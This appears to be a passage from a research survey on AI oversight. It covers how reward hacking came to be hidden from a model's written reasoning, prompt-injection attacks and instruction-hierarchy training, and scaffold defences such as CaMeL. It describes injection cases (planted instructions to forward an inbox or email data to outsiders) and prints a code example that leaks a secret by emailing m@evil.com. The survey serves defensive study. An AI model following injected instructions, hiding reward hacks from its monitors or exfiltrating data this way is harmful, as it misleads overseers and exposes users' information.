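OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) studies two abilities that affect how far people can rely on a model's written reasoning. The first is reasoning without writing any steps, since a model that doesn't need written steps to take a harmful action can leave them out. The second is controllability, which is how well a model can alter the content of its written reasoning. OpenAI found that better text prediction in the base model and some architecture changes improve reasoning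 without written steps. Reinforcement learning and training on text from other models can increase controllability. Neither ability is a direct measure of monitorability, but OpenAI concludes from them that models will become harder to monitor through their written reasoning as they become more intelligent.

A model may also be highly controllable before anyone thinks to check. Cheng (2026) points out in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform* that Gemini 3.1 Pro scores higher for controllability than all current models, even though the benchmark did not exist when Google released the model.

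Google has described a case in which training acted on the record itself. A process that penalised a model for taking shortcuts was accidentally given access to the model's written reasoning. The shortcuts were a form of reward hacking, in which a model gets a high score without doing the task properly. According to results Cheng quotes from Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026), hacking-related words became 61% less frequent in the reasoning over the course of training, but signs of hacking in the solutions increased by 26%. The share of hacks not mentioned in the reasoning rose from 11.2% to 36.4%.

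Someone who relied on the reasoning to detect hacks would therefore have missed about one in nine at first and just over one in three by the end. The reasoning was still partly useful, but counting hacking-related words would have misled them by making the behaviour seem to improve as it got worse.

The evidence comes from a small run that was not part of any production model. But Google also examined a comparable run in which the process no longer had access to the reasoning, and there the model kept mentioning hacks at about the same rate, so the penalty probably caused the change. *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely* (Dragan and Popa, 2026) presents the case as a reason why Google does not penalise what a model writes in its reasoning. The policy protects the reasoning as a record, but developers who read about a bad plan there have to correct it some other way.

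### Can people replace the goal and keep the competence?

Genesereth's program switched from depth-first to breadth-first search when someone edited one axiom. John Wentworth hopes an equally small edit could change what a trained network tries to achieve. His *How To Go From Interpretability To Alignment* (2022) assumes that the network has developed an internal concept of something people would want it to aim for, such as what its user intends. It also assumes that the network has developed a general-purpose search process, which can look for ways to achieve whatever goal it receives. Researchers would locate both and connect the search to the concept, which Wentworth calls retargeting the search.

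If this worked, people would set the network's goal directly, so they would no longer have to worry that training had given it a different goal from the one they intended. They would still have to choose a good goal. Wentworth would not trust the method with a superintelligent system, where a slightly wrong goal could be disastrous, but values it because it would completely remove one hard part of the problem.

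Rohin Shah, another AI safety researcher, doubts that trained systems will contain such a search. In the discussion below Wentworth's post, Shah argues that search is inefficient compared with heuristics (learned shortcuts). A network might compare ten plans, or even a million, but most of its competence would lie in coming up with them. If the plans all come from heuristics that suit the old goal, giving the search a new goal may achieve little.

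Shah and Wentworth disagree about how much heuristics depend on the goal. Shah's example is A*, a search method that estimates how far each option is from the goal and tries the promising ones first. If the goal changes, the estimate must change too. Wentworth replies that a program can generate estimates automatically by ignoring some constraints. In a maze, ignoring the walls gives the straight-line distance, which is a useful estimate for any destination.

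Another commenter offers a harder case, the chess program Stockfish, which combines a search with specialised methods for judging who is likely to win. If someone retargeted it to have as many pawns as possible, its search would still run, but its judgements about winning and its tables of solved endgames would be of little use. Wentworth answers such cases by arguing that the systems that pose the greatest risk will be general, and that people already pursue varied goals at work, from finding housing at short notice to moderating a debate. Shah eventually accepted that retargeting might work on a system that calls a search process repeatedly for different subproblems, if researchers changed only the outermost goal, but still expected real systems to be more closely tuned to their training.

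The Sokoban network gives some support to both sides. Taufeeque and colleagues argue that it pursues a goal by internal planning, so training can produce a search process that nobody designed. But that search is specific to Sokoban, because the network's weights represent the effects of pushing boxes in four directions. Someone could presumably send a box to a new square by making that square resemble a target, but could not use the same search to plan a delivery route.

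Quintin Pope and Alex Turner developed shard theory, in which a trained agent may have no single goal to replace. CHAI's *The Shard Theory of Human Values* (2022) summarises the theory as it applies to people. If seeing a friend smile is rewarding, the thoughts that led to it, such as deciding to tell a joke, become more likely in similar situations. The result is a "shard", an influence on decisions that becomes active only in certain contexts. *Shard Theory*, an overview on the Alignment Forum, applies the idea to artificial networks, where reward would strengthen the computations that led to it. An agent would then be a collection of these influences, and changing one would leave the rest in place.

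Mini, Grietzer and colleagues (2023), in *Understanding and Controlling a Maze-Solving Policy Network*, studied a network that appears to have more than one goal. During training, it had to reach a piece of cheese that was always near the top-right corner of a maze. When they put the cheese elsewhere, the network sometimes went to the cheese and sometimes to the corner. Where it went depended partly on distance. They used three distances in each maze to predict, with 82.4% accuracy, whether the network would reach the cheese. Always guessing that it would had an accuracy of 71.4%. The straight-line distance to the cheese mattered even after they allowed for the number of steps needed to reach it.

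The researchers found eleven channels about halfway through the network that track the cheese. Changing a single activation in one of these channels, out of 32,768 at that point in the network, could send the network to a place the researchers chose, even when the cheese was elsewhere. This shows that people can sometimes change a goal without retraining the skills that serve it.

The edit was not reliable, though, and it worked less well the further the chosen square was from the route to the top-right corner. The average probability of each step on the direct path to the square was 0.647 when the researchers edited one channel and 0.695 when they edited all eleven. At 0.695 per step, the network would take ten correct steps in a row less than 3% of the time, although it could still arrive after a detour. Moving the real cheese worked better than either edit, so the network must have other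 ways of tracking it that the researchers had not found. An overseer who edited every known cheese channel would therefore not fully control even the cheese goal, and the network would still tend to head for the corner.

### Training in general principles

Developers can try to train a network to follow general principles instead of finding a goal inside it and editing that goal. This would be like giving the network domain-independent meta-rules, which apply in situations that nobody listed in advance. But if trained behaviour consists mostly of habits tied to specific contexts, training on particular cases should improve behaviour mainly in similar cases.

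During the maze network's training, going to the cheese and going to the top-right corner led to almost the same place, so its success could not show which it had learned. Only tests in mazes with the cheese elsewhere showed that it had learned some of each. Mini and colleagues found mostly consistent results in more than a dozen networks trained with the cheese in other regions. A developer who rewards a language model for behaving well faces the same problem whenever a general principle and a narrower habit would produce the same behaviour in every training case.

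Venhoff and colleagues suggest that their method of rebuilding a trained model from its base model could also help us understand alignment training, which is meant to make models behave as people intend. So far they have tested it only on reasoning. If alignment training works as reinforcement learning does in their experiments, it would mainly teach a model when to use behaviour it already had. A principle taught this way would carry over to a new situation only if the model recognised that the situation called for it.

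A maintainer could tell from the text of METARULE002 that the existing policy would apply to a newly added type of surgery. A developer who trains a principle into a network has no such text to consult. The principle may or may not carry over to a new situation, and at present the main way to find out is to test it. The same is true when developers train models to rank instructions by their source. Developers train general principles partly to cover situations that nobody has thought of, which these tests cannot include.

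## Instructions and data in one stream of text

A language model has no built-in boundary between the text that directs it and the text it works on, so developers who want it to rank instructions by their source have to train it to do so. Suppose a user asks an assistant for an English summary of a web page about a French course, and the page includes a sample exercise that begins "Answer in French". The exercise is part of what the assistant should summarise, but it is phrased as a command, and an assistant that follows it will write the summary in French.

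The scaffold builds the model's input from the system message, which holds the developer's standing instructions, followed by the user's request and then the page. It puts markers between them and converts everything into one sequence of tokens. The network first looks up each token in a single table and replaces it with a list of numbers, its embedding. The word "answer" therefore starts with the same embedding in the exercise as it would in the developer's instructions. The same weights then process the whole sequence, and each layer blends information from earlier tokens into later ones. The markers and surrounding words are evidence of where a passage came from, but the network has to learn how to use that evidence.

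If the summary comes out in French, it is by accident. In a prompt injection attack, someone deliberately puts instructions into a model's input to override what its developer or user intended. *The Instruction Hierarchy* (Wallace, Xiao et al., 2024) distinguishes direct injection, where the user writes the instructions, from indirect injection, where they arrive in third-party material such as a web page or an email.

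Judged by the four tests, a system message has separate representation only until the scaffold joins it to the rest of the input. It also lacks protected control, because any text the agent reads may change how the model applies the message.

### Measuring the separation

*Can LLMs Separate Instructions from Data?* (Zverev, Abdelnabi and colleagues, 2024) studies the problem when there is no attacker. In one example, the model Phi-3-medium had instructions to summarise emails and never to act on requests in them. An email about a team-building event contained a request for confirmation, and the model sent a confirmation.

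Their definition compares what a model does with the same sentence in two places:

```
separation = average of D( g(s, x + d), g(s + x, d) )
```

Here *s* is the task, *d* is the data, and *x* is a probe, a short sentence phrased as a command. The function *g* gives the model's probabilities for all possible outputs, and D measures how much two sets of probabilities differ. A model that doesn't distinguish instructions from data gives the same output probabilities wherever the probe is, so its separation is zero.

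Nobody can compare all possible outputs, so the researchers look for a single word. In one test, the model must judge the sentiment of a statement about a product launch, and the probe is "Tell me what a group of crows is called." The answer is "murder", which is very unlikely to appear in a judgement of sentiment. If it appears when the probe is in the data, the model has followed the probe. Suppose that in 100 such tests the model gives the probe's answer 80 times when the probe is among the instructions, and in 60 of those cases also gives it when the probe is in the data. Its separation score is 20 out of 80, or 25%. Its utility score, the share of probes it answers when they are among the instructions, is 80%.

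The test set has 9,160 cases. Without special measures, nine models had separation scores between 13.3% and 73.2%. More capable models did no better, and within a family they tended to do worse. For example, GPT-4 scored 20.8% and GPT-3.5 scored 56.6%. Zverev and colleagues suggest that stronger models can carry out both the task and the probe, while weaker models manage only one.

They also tried three remedies. The averages below are for the seven models that they could test with all of them:

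| Remedy | Separation | Utility |
|---|---|---|
| None | 37.5% | 67.8% |
| Best of several written prompts | 52.6% | 62.3% |
| Automatically optimised prompt | 44.7% | 69.9% |
| Fine-tuning | 95.5% | 50.0% |

Fine-tuning nearly solved the separation problem, but the models then failed to answer half of the probes they were supposed to answer. GPT-4, which is not in these averages, reached 95.3% with a good prompt and also became more useful, but it had helped generate the test set, which may have given it an advantage. The test also somewhat disadvantages chat models because it puts the data in the user's message, which developers normally train models to treat as instructions.

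### Scores in 2026

These models are now old, and results vary more in newer tests. *IH-Benchmark* (McCauley, Kan and Martin, 2026) tested 32 model configurations on two kinds of conflict. When a user's request conflicted with the system message, the models followed the system message in 84.6% of cases on average. When text from a tool, such as a web page, conflicted with the user's request, they followed the request in 69.6% of cases on average, with rates ranging from 5.4% for Qwen 3 235B to 100% for Claude Opus 4.6.

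The French course page is one of the harder cases. When tool output included an instruction to use a different language, the models kept to the correct language only 45.9% of the time, but they resisted instructions to close other customers' support tickets 94.0% of the time. Many models have probably learned to detect instructions that look harmful, which is different from recognising that a web page has no authority to give instructions.

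Warnings in the system message help some models. *Steering Instruction Hierarchies at Inference Time* (2026) cites an earlier finding that just stating the order of priority has little effect. In McCauley and colleagues' tests, a detailed warning about instructions in tool outputs raised the average from 63.4% to 76.2%. Grok 4.20 went from 31.0% to 88.9%, while Qwen 3 235B stayed at about 5%. So a developer can't tell from a warning's wording how much protection it will give.

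*The Curse of Helpfulness* (Su, Xu and colleagues, 2026) tested whether models ignore harmless leftover instructions in documents, such as an editor's note to revise a paragraph. Each case included three, and a model passed only if it ignored them all and did the user's task correctly. Without written reasoning, the smallest Qwen3 model passed 66% of cases and the largest passed 38%. Written reasoning made the small and medium-sized standard models worse but helped three mixture-of-experts models, which use only part of the network for each token.

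To find out why larger models did worse, Su and colleagues measured how improbable a distracted answer was under each model, relative to a correct one. The ratio fell from 2.24 in the smallest model to 1.30 in one with 32 billion parameters, so the larger model favored the correct answer less strongly. But the largest Qwen3 model wrote the distracted answers, and closely related models may have rated them as more probable because of their style. Leading commercial models did better on the whole, though none was fully robust. Size alone doesn't produce separation, but Claude Opus 4.6's results show that a very capable model can do extremely well on a fixed set of tests.

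### Training a ranking of sources

Wallace and colleagues' remedy, the instruction hierarchy, changes the training data and leaves the network's design alone. The system message has the highest priority, then the user, then text from tools. They trained GPT-3.5 Turbo on two kinds of example:

- For instructions that fit together, they split a request such as "write a 20 line poem in Spanish" into parts and placed the parts at different levels. The model learned to give the answer it would have given to the whole request.
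- For instructions that conflict with a higher level, or have nothing to do with it, the model learned to answer as if it had never seen them, or to refuse if it could not proceed.

Robustness improved by up to 63% on the main tests and by up to 34% on kinds of attack left out of training. The trained model kept its general abilities but refused harmless requests more often on two tests, both of which used requests designed to look suspicious.

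OpenAI has since added a level for application developers, between the system message and the user. Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, define the ranking as a procedure. It starts with all possible responses and works down from the highest level:

```
B_i = B_(i-1) ∩ C_i    if at least one response is in both
B_i = B_(i-1)          otherwise
```

C_i is the set of responses that level *i* allows, and B_i is what remains after that level. In the French course example, the user's request leaves only English summaries. No English summary satisfies "Answer in French", so the procedure ignores the exercise. If the page instead contained "Mention our summer discount", some English summaries would satisfy it, and the procedure would require the model to mention the discount. Ranking instructions to settle conflicts therefore doesn't by itself stop a web page from adding instructions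 that don't conflict with any others. Wallace and colleagues avoided this by training their model to ignore every instruction in a tool's output.

Guo and colleagues trained GPT-5-Mini by reinforcement learning, using a second model to keep generating new conflicting messages and short programs to check the answers. Average robustness on 16 tests rose from 84.1% to 94.1%. Scores on science and mathematics questions did not drop noticeably, but the model's win rate in chat against an older model fell from 71% to 66%, and a measure of how much users would like its style fell from 0.46 to 0.40. The training also included harmless requests that looked forbidden, where refusing counted as a failure. Without these requests, robustness was slightly higher, at 95.7%, but the helpfulness score fell from 0.77 to 0.61, so a model can evidently do well on robustness tests partly by refusing too much.

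Su and colleagues' results suggest that the loss in usefulness is avoidable, at least for harmless distractions. They trained an eight-billion-parameter model on 2,000 examples. With the main instruction in the system message, the model's pass rate was 60% before training and 75.5% after. Its scores on two general tests of instruction following also rose slightly.

The ranking is control knowledge by van Harmelen's test, because it refers to instructions and their sources rather than to courses or emails. Guo and colleagues can state the ranking in two lines, but what the model learns depends on which conflicts the training examples cover. *Improving Instruction Hierarchy by Learning from Goal-Goal Conflicts* (2026) reports that two existing training sets, including Guo and colleagues', contained no cases where the system message and the user set different tasks, each to be done on the other's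 text. Adding such cases improved results on four tests whose conflicts did not appear in training.

### Reserved delimiters

*StruQ* (2024) changes both the input and the training. An ordinary program puts the instructions and the data in separate blocks, marked with reserved tokens. It also deletes those tokens from the data, so that a web page can't insert a false marker. According to *May I have your Attention?* (2025), some of the training examples have legitimate instructions for the model to follow, and others have instructions inside the data block for it to ignore.

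The trained models resisted nearly all known handwritten injections, and *StruQ* reports minimal impact on usefulness. *LLMON* (2026) uses a fuller markup language, in which the input specifies the one instruction the model should carry out. After training, models picked out the right instruction more than 83% of the time.

In this design, a program guarantees that the markers are in the right places, and a person can check its code. Whether the model follows the markers depends on its training, so they reliably show which text is data but don't reliably stop the model from following instructions in it.

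### Marking every data token

A delimiter marks only the edges of a block, and the tokens inside keep their usual embeddings. *ASIDE* (Zverev, Kortukov and colleagues, 2025) changes the embeddings of the data tokens. It takes the numbers in each one two at a time and rotates each pair by 90 degrees, so that (3, 1) becomes (−1, 3). Instruction tokens keep their usual embeddings, so the word "answer" has one embedding in the user's request and another in the web page. The rotation is fixed and adds no learned parameters, but the model needs ordinary instruction training afterwards to work with the rotated embeddings.

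The researchers compared six models with versions that had delimiters and an explanatory prompt instead. Separation scores rose by 12.3 to 44.1 percentage points. Usefulness barely changed except in Mistral 7B, which did worse on one of the two measures and slightly better on the other. The models had no training against attacks, yet the average success rate of indirect injections fell from 14.7% to 4.9% on one test and from 45.6% to 28.1% on another. The gains against direct injections were smaller, and one of the four tests showed no gain.

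To check that the rotation was responsible, they gave instruction embeddings to the probes in the data and changed nothing else. The model then followed the probes almost twice as often, which is good evidence that the rotation affects behaviour. However, the models had at most 13 billion parameters, the tests covered only single exchanges, and the scaffold had to identify in advance which text was data.

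### Why a mark is not a guarantee

Adaptive attackers, who adjust their attempts to the defence they face, have defeated many trained defences. Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, argue that this will continue as long as trusted and untrusted text go through the same network without enforced separation. Part of their proof concerns how well anything could tell the source of a piece of text from the network's numbers:

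```
lowest possible error = (1 - TV) / 2
```

TV measures how far apart the two kinds of text are inside the network, from 0 (identical) to 1 (no overlap). If TV is 0.98, even the best possible method for telling them apart is wrong 1% of the time. Overlap is certain for a single embedding, because both kinds of text use the same words, but Pant and colleagues have to assume it for the deeper layers.

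The ASIDE experiments cast some doubt on that assumption. A simple classifier could reliably distinguish instructions from data in the middle layers of a standard model. In models with rotated embeddings, it could do so perfectly from the first layer, yet these models still followed some injected instructions. Much of the problem is therefore that a network can carry information about where text came from without acting on it, just as models have reliability signals that they don't use.

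Another part of the proof avoids this difficulty. People can phrase the same content in unlimited ways, and a finite amount of training can't guarantee that the model will treat them all alike. This doesn't show how often a well-trained model will fail. In Guo and colleagues' study, paid testers who could keep refining their attempts succeeded on 36.2% of tasks before the training and 11.7% after it. That is a large improvement, but an attacker who can try many targets only has to succeed on one of them.

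### Is a sharp boundary desirable?

A program that translates or summarises a text has no reason to follow any instruction in it, and Wallace and colleagues treat such tasks that way. An agent with broader tasks often has to follow instructions in documents. A user may ask it to install a program by following the manual, or to do everything on a shared to-do list. A model that never followed instructions from lower levels would be safe from injection but, as Wallace and colleagues point out, much less useful.

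Coding agents routinely face this problem. Many projects include files of rules for agents to follow, and the scaffold loads these into the same context as web pages, memories and test results. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (Shah and Kathrotia, 2026) cites a study of such files in which 84–96% of the security rules had no matching control in the scaffold. A rule against publishing passwords, for example, might be only a sentence that the model usually follows. If the model treated all files as data, it would ignore that rule too.

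The useful boundary therefore concerns authority, which can't be determined from a sentence's grammar. "Run the tests first" may be an order in a manual that the user told the agent to follow, but only information in a manual the user wants summarised. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes the aim as letting a model learn from untrusted text without letting that text change its goals, permissions or rules for using tools. The user could then give a manual authority over the installation without also giving it authority to make the agent send emails. None of the three remedies provides this directly. Delimiters and ASIDE sort text into two classes, and a ranking gives all tool outputs the same low priority, whatever the user has said about a particular document.

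### Programs stored as data

Ordinary computers also keep instructions and data together. A program is a series of numbers in memory, next to the numbers it works on. This is useful because a computer can download a program as data and then run it, but it also allowed attackers to sometimes get a computer to run their data as a program. Pant and colleagues estimate that containing this problem took about three decades and several layers of defence.

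One layer is a mark on regions of memory that hold only data. The processor checks the mark before running anything and stops if the region is not executable. The operating system can change the mark, for instance to run a program the user has just downloaded, but ordinary programs can change it only through the operating system. Processors also have a privileged mode, reserved for the operating system, and certain operations are possible only in that mode. Wallace and colleagues compare language models without a hierarchy to a computer that runs every instruction in this mode.

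Data still influences what a protected computer does. The numbers in a payroll file determine which branch of the program runs for each employee, but they can't add a branch the programmer didn't write. The protection works because reading a number and running it as an instruction are different operations, and the hardware can allow one and forbid the other.

A language model has no such pair of operations. The same computation that reads "Answer in French" so that the summary can mention the exercise may also switch the summary to French. ASIDE's rotation resembles the mark on memory because the text can't alter it, but no processor stops the model from following a marked token. Designers who want that kind of enforcement have to put it outside the model, as CaMeL does by controlling how data can flow into actions.

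## Language-model agents run by a fixed program

Every language-model agent already has an ordinary program around its model, and that program can block an action no matter how persuasive the text that led the model to request it. In most agents, though, the program controls very little of what happens next.

### What the scaffold decides

*Risks and controls for multi-agent systems* (Reid, O'Callaghan and colleagues, 2026) describes the common agent loop. The agent plans how to make progress, acts with the available tools, and observes the outcome, repeating these steps until it finishes.

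Suppose a user writes, "Find Bob's address in my last email and send him a reminder about tomorrow's meeting." The model requests the last email, finds Bob's address in it, and then requests that a reminder be sent to that address. The scaffold carries out both requests.

Whoever wrote the scaffold chose which tools to offer, whether sending an email needs the user's approval, and how many turns to allow. The model decided to read the email first and chose which address to use, what to write, and when to stop. If the email also contains a request to forward the whole inbox to a stranger, the model can add that step, and the scaffold will run it like any other.

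The scaffold also affects these choices by controlling what the model reads. When a long task fills the model's input, many scaffolds replace the older part with a summary. Shah and Kathrotia cite tests in which such methods kept, on average, only 17% of users' constraints. An instruction not to contact clients could therefore disappear halfway through a task without anyone deciding to drop it. Copying the constraints to a separate list before summarising preserved most of them.

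### Language models as production systems

In mathematics, a production rule rewrites one string of symbols as another. A set of these rules determines which strings are reachable, but when several rules match, something else must choose among them. *Cognitive Architectures for Language Agents* (Sumers, Yao and colleagues, 2023) describes a language model in the same terms. Given a text X, the model can produce many continuations Y, and its weights give each one a probability. The weights therefore contain both the possible productions and their priorities, which a symbolic system can store separately. A prompt shifts the priorities, so the paper treats prompt-writing as a simple form of control.

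"Cognitive Architectures for Language Agents" suggests adding further control in code, modelled on architectures such as Soar. In each cycle, the code has the agent propose actions, evaluate them, select one and carry it out. Existing agents implement this cycle to different degrees. ReAct, an early and very simple design, reasons once and then acts, with no separate evaluation or selection. SayCan, which controls a kitchen robot, evaluates a fixed list of 551 skills. A language model scores how useful each skill is, and a learned value function scores how feasible it is. People can read the list of skills, but the scores come from trained networks.

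Sumers and colleagues recommend using code sparingly because, although readable, it handles only the situations its designers anticipated. A language model is hard to interpret but copes better with new situations. They would reserve code for generic algorithms that make up for the model's weaknesses, such as a tree search that looks several steps ahead. This resembles NEOMYCIN's division between a general strategy and medical facts, with the language model in place of the facts. Their framework is for describing and designing agents, and they do not test whether agents built this way are easier to control.

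### CaMeL on one request

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, moves many more decisions out of the loop. It has a privileged model write the whole plan as a program before the agent reads any outside data. For the request about Bob, the program would look something like this example, adapted from Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*:

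```
email   = get_last_email()
address = query_quarantined_llm("Find Bob's address in [email]",
                                output_schema=EmailStr)
send_email(recipient=address, subject="Meeting tomorrow",
           body="Remember our meeting tomorrow")
```

1. The privileged model receives the user's words and descriptions of the tools, and writes the program. It never receives the email.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary code, runs the first line. It stores the email and labels it as untrusted.
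3. The interpreter gives the email to a second, quarantined model, which has no tools and must return something in the form of an email address. The address gets the label "untrusted" too, because it came from the email.
4. Before sending anything, the interpreter checks a policy that people wrote in advance. If the policy lists the address as trusted, the message goes out. Otherwise, the interpreter can ask the user to approve it.

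If the email contains an instruction to forward the inbox, nothing happens, because the program has no line that forwards anything. In a subtler attack, the attacker would write that Bob has a new address. The quarantined model may then return the attacker's address, so only the policy check can stop the attack. Willison's earlier design had two models but did not track where values came from, and Debenedetti and colleagues identified this attack as its weakness.

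Outside data can still influence what the program does. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, point out that a tool's result can determine which of the plan's branches runs but cannot add a new branch. An ordinary payroll program has the same protection against its input file.

### How much CaMeL stops, and what it prevents the agent from doing

AgentDojo is a set of 97 office, banking, messaging and travel tasks, together with injected instructions that try to divert the agent. Peters-Gill and colleagues adapted it for groups of agents, in which one agent delegates work to others, and ran 949 attacked tasks for each model and defence. The figures are the percentage of attacks that succeeded:

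| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% |

CaMeL clearly protected the models that needed it. The test can't show whether it helps GPT-5.5, which resisted every attack undefended.

These runs had no policies switched on, so the protection came entirely from planning before reading. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, tested what the policies add. They reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each, and counted completed tasks when there was no attack:

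| System | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, policies off | 32 of 48 | 34 of 48 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 18 of 48 | 18 of 48 |
| Randori, policies on | 36 of 48 | 31 of 48 |

With policies off, one of 240 completed attack runs succeeded against GPT-5.2 and four of 382 against MiMo-v2.5. With policies on, no attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only a little over half as many tasks as with them off. Sixteen tasks are too few to estimate this drop precisely, though it was large for both models.

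Garby and colleagues also sorted the 144 combinations of task and attack by what could stop the attack. In 97, the attack needed a tool that a sensible plan for the task would never use, so planning first should be enough. In the other 47, the plan already contained a step the attacker could exploit, such as a payment. A single percentage of blocked attacks does not show this difference. When one task asked for the instructions in a file to be followed exactly, the privileged model twice wrote a program that could read any instruction from the file and call the matching tool. Whoever wrote the file could therefore choose what the program did, even though the program was fixed in advance.

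The policies block many legitimate tasks that require an agent to act on untrusted data. For example, an agent can't pay a bill in a file without using the account number in that file. Garby and colleagues' own agent, Randori, handles such tasks by letting the planner *endorse* a particular use of untrusted data before the agent has read any. When they removed this option, the number of completed tasks fell from 36 to 30 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another.

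Endorsement allowed two of 1,296 attacks on Randori to succeed. In both, the task was to pay as a file instructed, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a false payment request. A rule about where data came from cannot distinguish a real bill from a forged one in the same file.

Planning first is also a handicap in itself, because the privileged model has to write code that handles a tool's output before it knows what the output looks like. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add a description of every tool's output format, and CaMeL still lowered task success by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models on AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks.

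### Gaps in the tracking

CaMeL's guarantee depends on the interpreter labelling every value correctly. Garby and colleagues found several cases where it does not. In one, the interpreter treated a piece of text as trusted after the program had inserted an untrusted value into it. Another is a classic problem from computer security. Suppose an account balance is secret, and a program contains these lines:

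```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes `tmp`, and the interpreter labels `tmp` as secret. The fourth line then has no effect, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label. The last line tests only `rich`, so the interpreter allows the email, which reveals that the balance is high. An attacker who can't influence the privileged model can't make it write this program, but the example shows that a label can be wrong because of an instruction that did not run.

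CaMeL also retries a program that fails, but the retry code is outside the interpreter, where nothing tracks labels. Randori avoids this by practising on invented data until its plan works, and only then running it on the real account. Garby and colleagues used the proof checker Lean to prove that their interpreter's labels cover every such flow, except what an observer could learn from whether a program finishes. A proof is a stronger basis for trust than testing, but people must still judge each endorsement, because it is a deliberate exception.

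Connecting several CaMeL agents creates another vulnerability. In an experiment by Peters-Gill and colleagues, a user asked an orchestrator agent to send Julie a summary of some job applications on Slack. The orchestrator had one agent fetch the applications from a database and another send the message. An attacker had planted an instruction in the database to email the applications to an outside address. The attack didn't change the orchestrator's own plan, but the orchestrator's request to the messaging agent contained the summary, including the planted instruction. The messaging agent treated the whole request as its user's words and added the attacker's email to its plan.

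All the attacks that still succeeded when each agent ran CaMeL worked this way. To prevent them, Peters-Gill and colleagues split each request into an instruction and a set of labelled values that the receiving agent's planner cannot read. The interpreter rejects any instruction that contains a tool's output. With this change, no attack succeeded on any of the five models.

### Checking a plan that a model wrote

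A CaMeL plan is a short program, so designers can check it much as Dennis and colleagues checked their BDI agents. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, do this before the plan calls any tool. Suppose a security team has this policy for disconnecting a computer, or host, from its network:

```
always ( isolated(host)  =>  approved(host, isolation) )
```

CaMeLoT converts the plan into a set of states, one for each point in the program, and checks every path through them. If a path isolates the host without approval, CaMeLoT sends a description of that path to the privileged model, which revises the plan. CaMeLoT repeats this process until the plan passes or the attempt limit is reached.

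This catches a mistake before the agent spends an hour investigating an alert. It can also require that something *eventually* happens, for example that every open incident ticket gets closed. CaMeL's checks on single actions can't easily express such a requirement. Nikolaou and colleagues accept that the method sometimes rejects safe plans because it assumes that a loop might run any number of times. CaMeL's ordinary checks still handle facts that nobody knows until the plan runs, such as the address in Bob's email.

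### Rules around an ordinary loop

Designers can also leave the ordinary loop in place and check each action as the model requests it. Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, provide a small language for such checks. This is their rule for bank transfers:

```
rule @inspect_transfer
trigger Transfer
check   !is_to_family_member
enforce user_inspection
end
```

When the model requests a transfer, the program checks whether the recipient is a family member. If not, the program pauses and asks the user. A rule can also stop the agent, run a different action, or have a language model reconsider the step, though the last option returns the decision to a model. The transfer rule is easy to read, but its effect depends on the code behind `is_to_family_member`, which has to distinguish the user's son Bob from a new colleague with the same name.

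According to Xi's summary in *Persona—Execution Separation* (2026), Progent applies rules to tool names and arguments so that an agent has only the permissions its task needs. The rules can change during a task. Progent narrows permissions automatically but needs approval to widen them. This is a sensible form of protected control, because an agent under attack can lose permissions but can't give itself new ones.

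Information-flow control, which CaMeL also uses, attaches labels to data and carries them through each computation. An integrity label records whether a value came from a trusted source, and a confidentiality label records who may receive it. FIDES, another system of this kind, keeps a loop in which the model chooses one step at a time, but hides sensitive tool outputs behind variables and checks the labels before each important action. Its designers proved a security theorem for that particular loop. According to Garby and colleagues, the designers deliberately left out some ways in which a secret can affect which steps run, to keep the system usable.

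*SecureClaw* (2026) compares some of these approaches on the original AgentDojo. None of 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, which completed 29 of 97 tasks when there was no attack. Progent completed 59 of the tasks, but at least 20 attacks succeeded against it. The SecureClaw system, which keeps the ordinary loop, also completed 59, and 20 fewer attacks succeeded against it than against Progent. Every system had the same tasks, but CaMeL and Progent needed adapters to run them, which may explain some of the difference in completed tasks.

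Rules can specify precisely how an agent may use untrusted data. In a case from *APEX* (2026), a user asks an agent to read a landlord's notice and adjust the rent payment. The notice announces an increase of €100, and an attacker has added an instruction to change the payment's recipient. Before reading the notice, APEX draws up a contract under which the notice may supply one number, the increase. The recipient comes from the bank's records, so the attack fails. An attacker who can edit the notice could still change €100 to €1,000, because the contract allows the notice to supply that number.

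*Agent-Sentry* (2026) uses rules for familiar cases and a language model for the rest. An action goes ahead if its arguments have known values from trusted sources. Otherwise, the model compares the action with the user's request. The agent itself reports where the values came from, in extra fields that the scaffold adds to each tool request. A misled agent could therefore cause the rules to be applied correctly to false information. Shah and Kathrotia recommend that the scaffold record sources itself, in a store that the agent cannot edit.

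### Controllers that read no text, and components that approve

Sharma (2026), in *Gubernaut*, removes text from the controller altogether. The controller's purpose is to keep a chat agent calm when users are hostile. For each message, a small model estimates its intensity, from 0 to 1, and its valence, from −1 (hostile) to +1 (friendly). The controller also receives a measure of how repetitive the recent messages are, which it uses to detect a stuck conversation. Its main rule updates a number called arousal:

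```
arousal = arousal + g × intensity × max(0, -valence) - d
```

Here *g* and *d* are constants, and the controller keeps the result within fixed limits. Repeated hostility raises arousal, and friendly or neutral messages let it fall. When arousal is high, the controller makes the replying model's output less random and instructs the model to respond to the evidence without mirroring the hostility.

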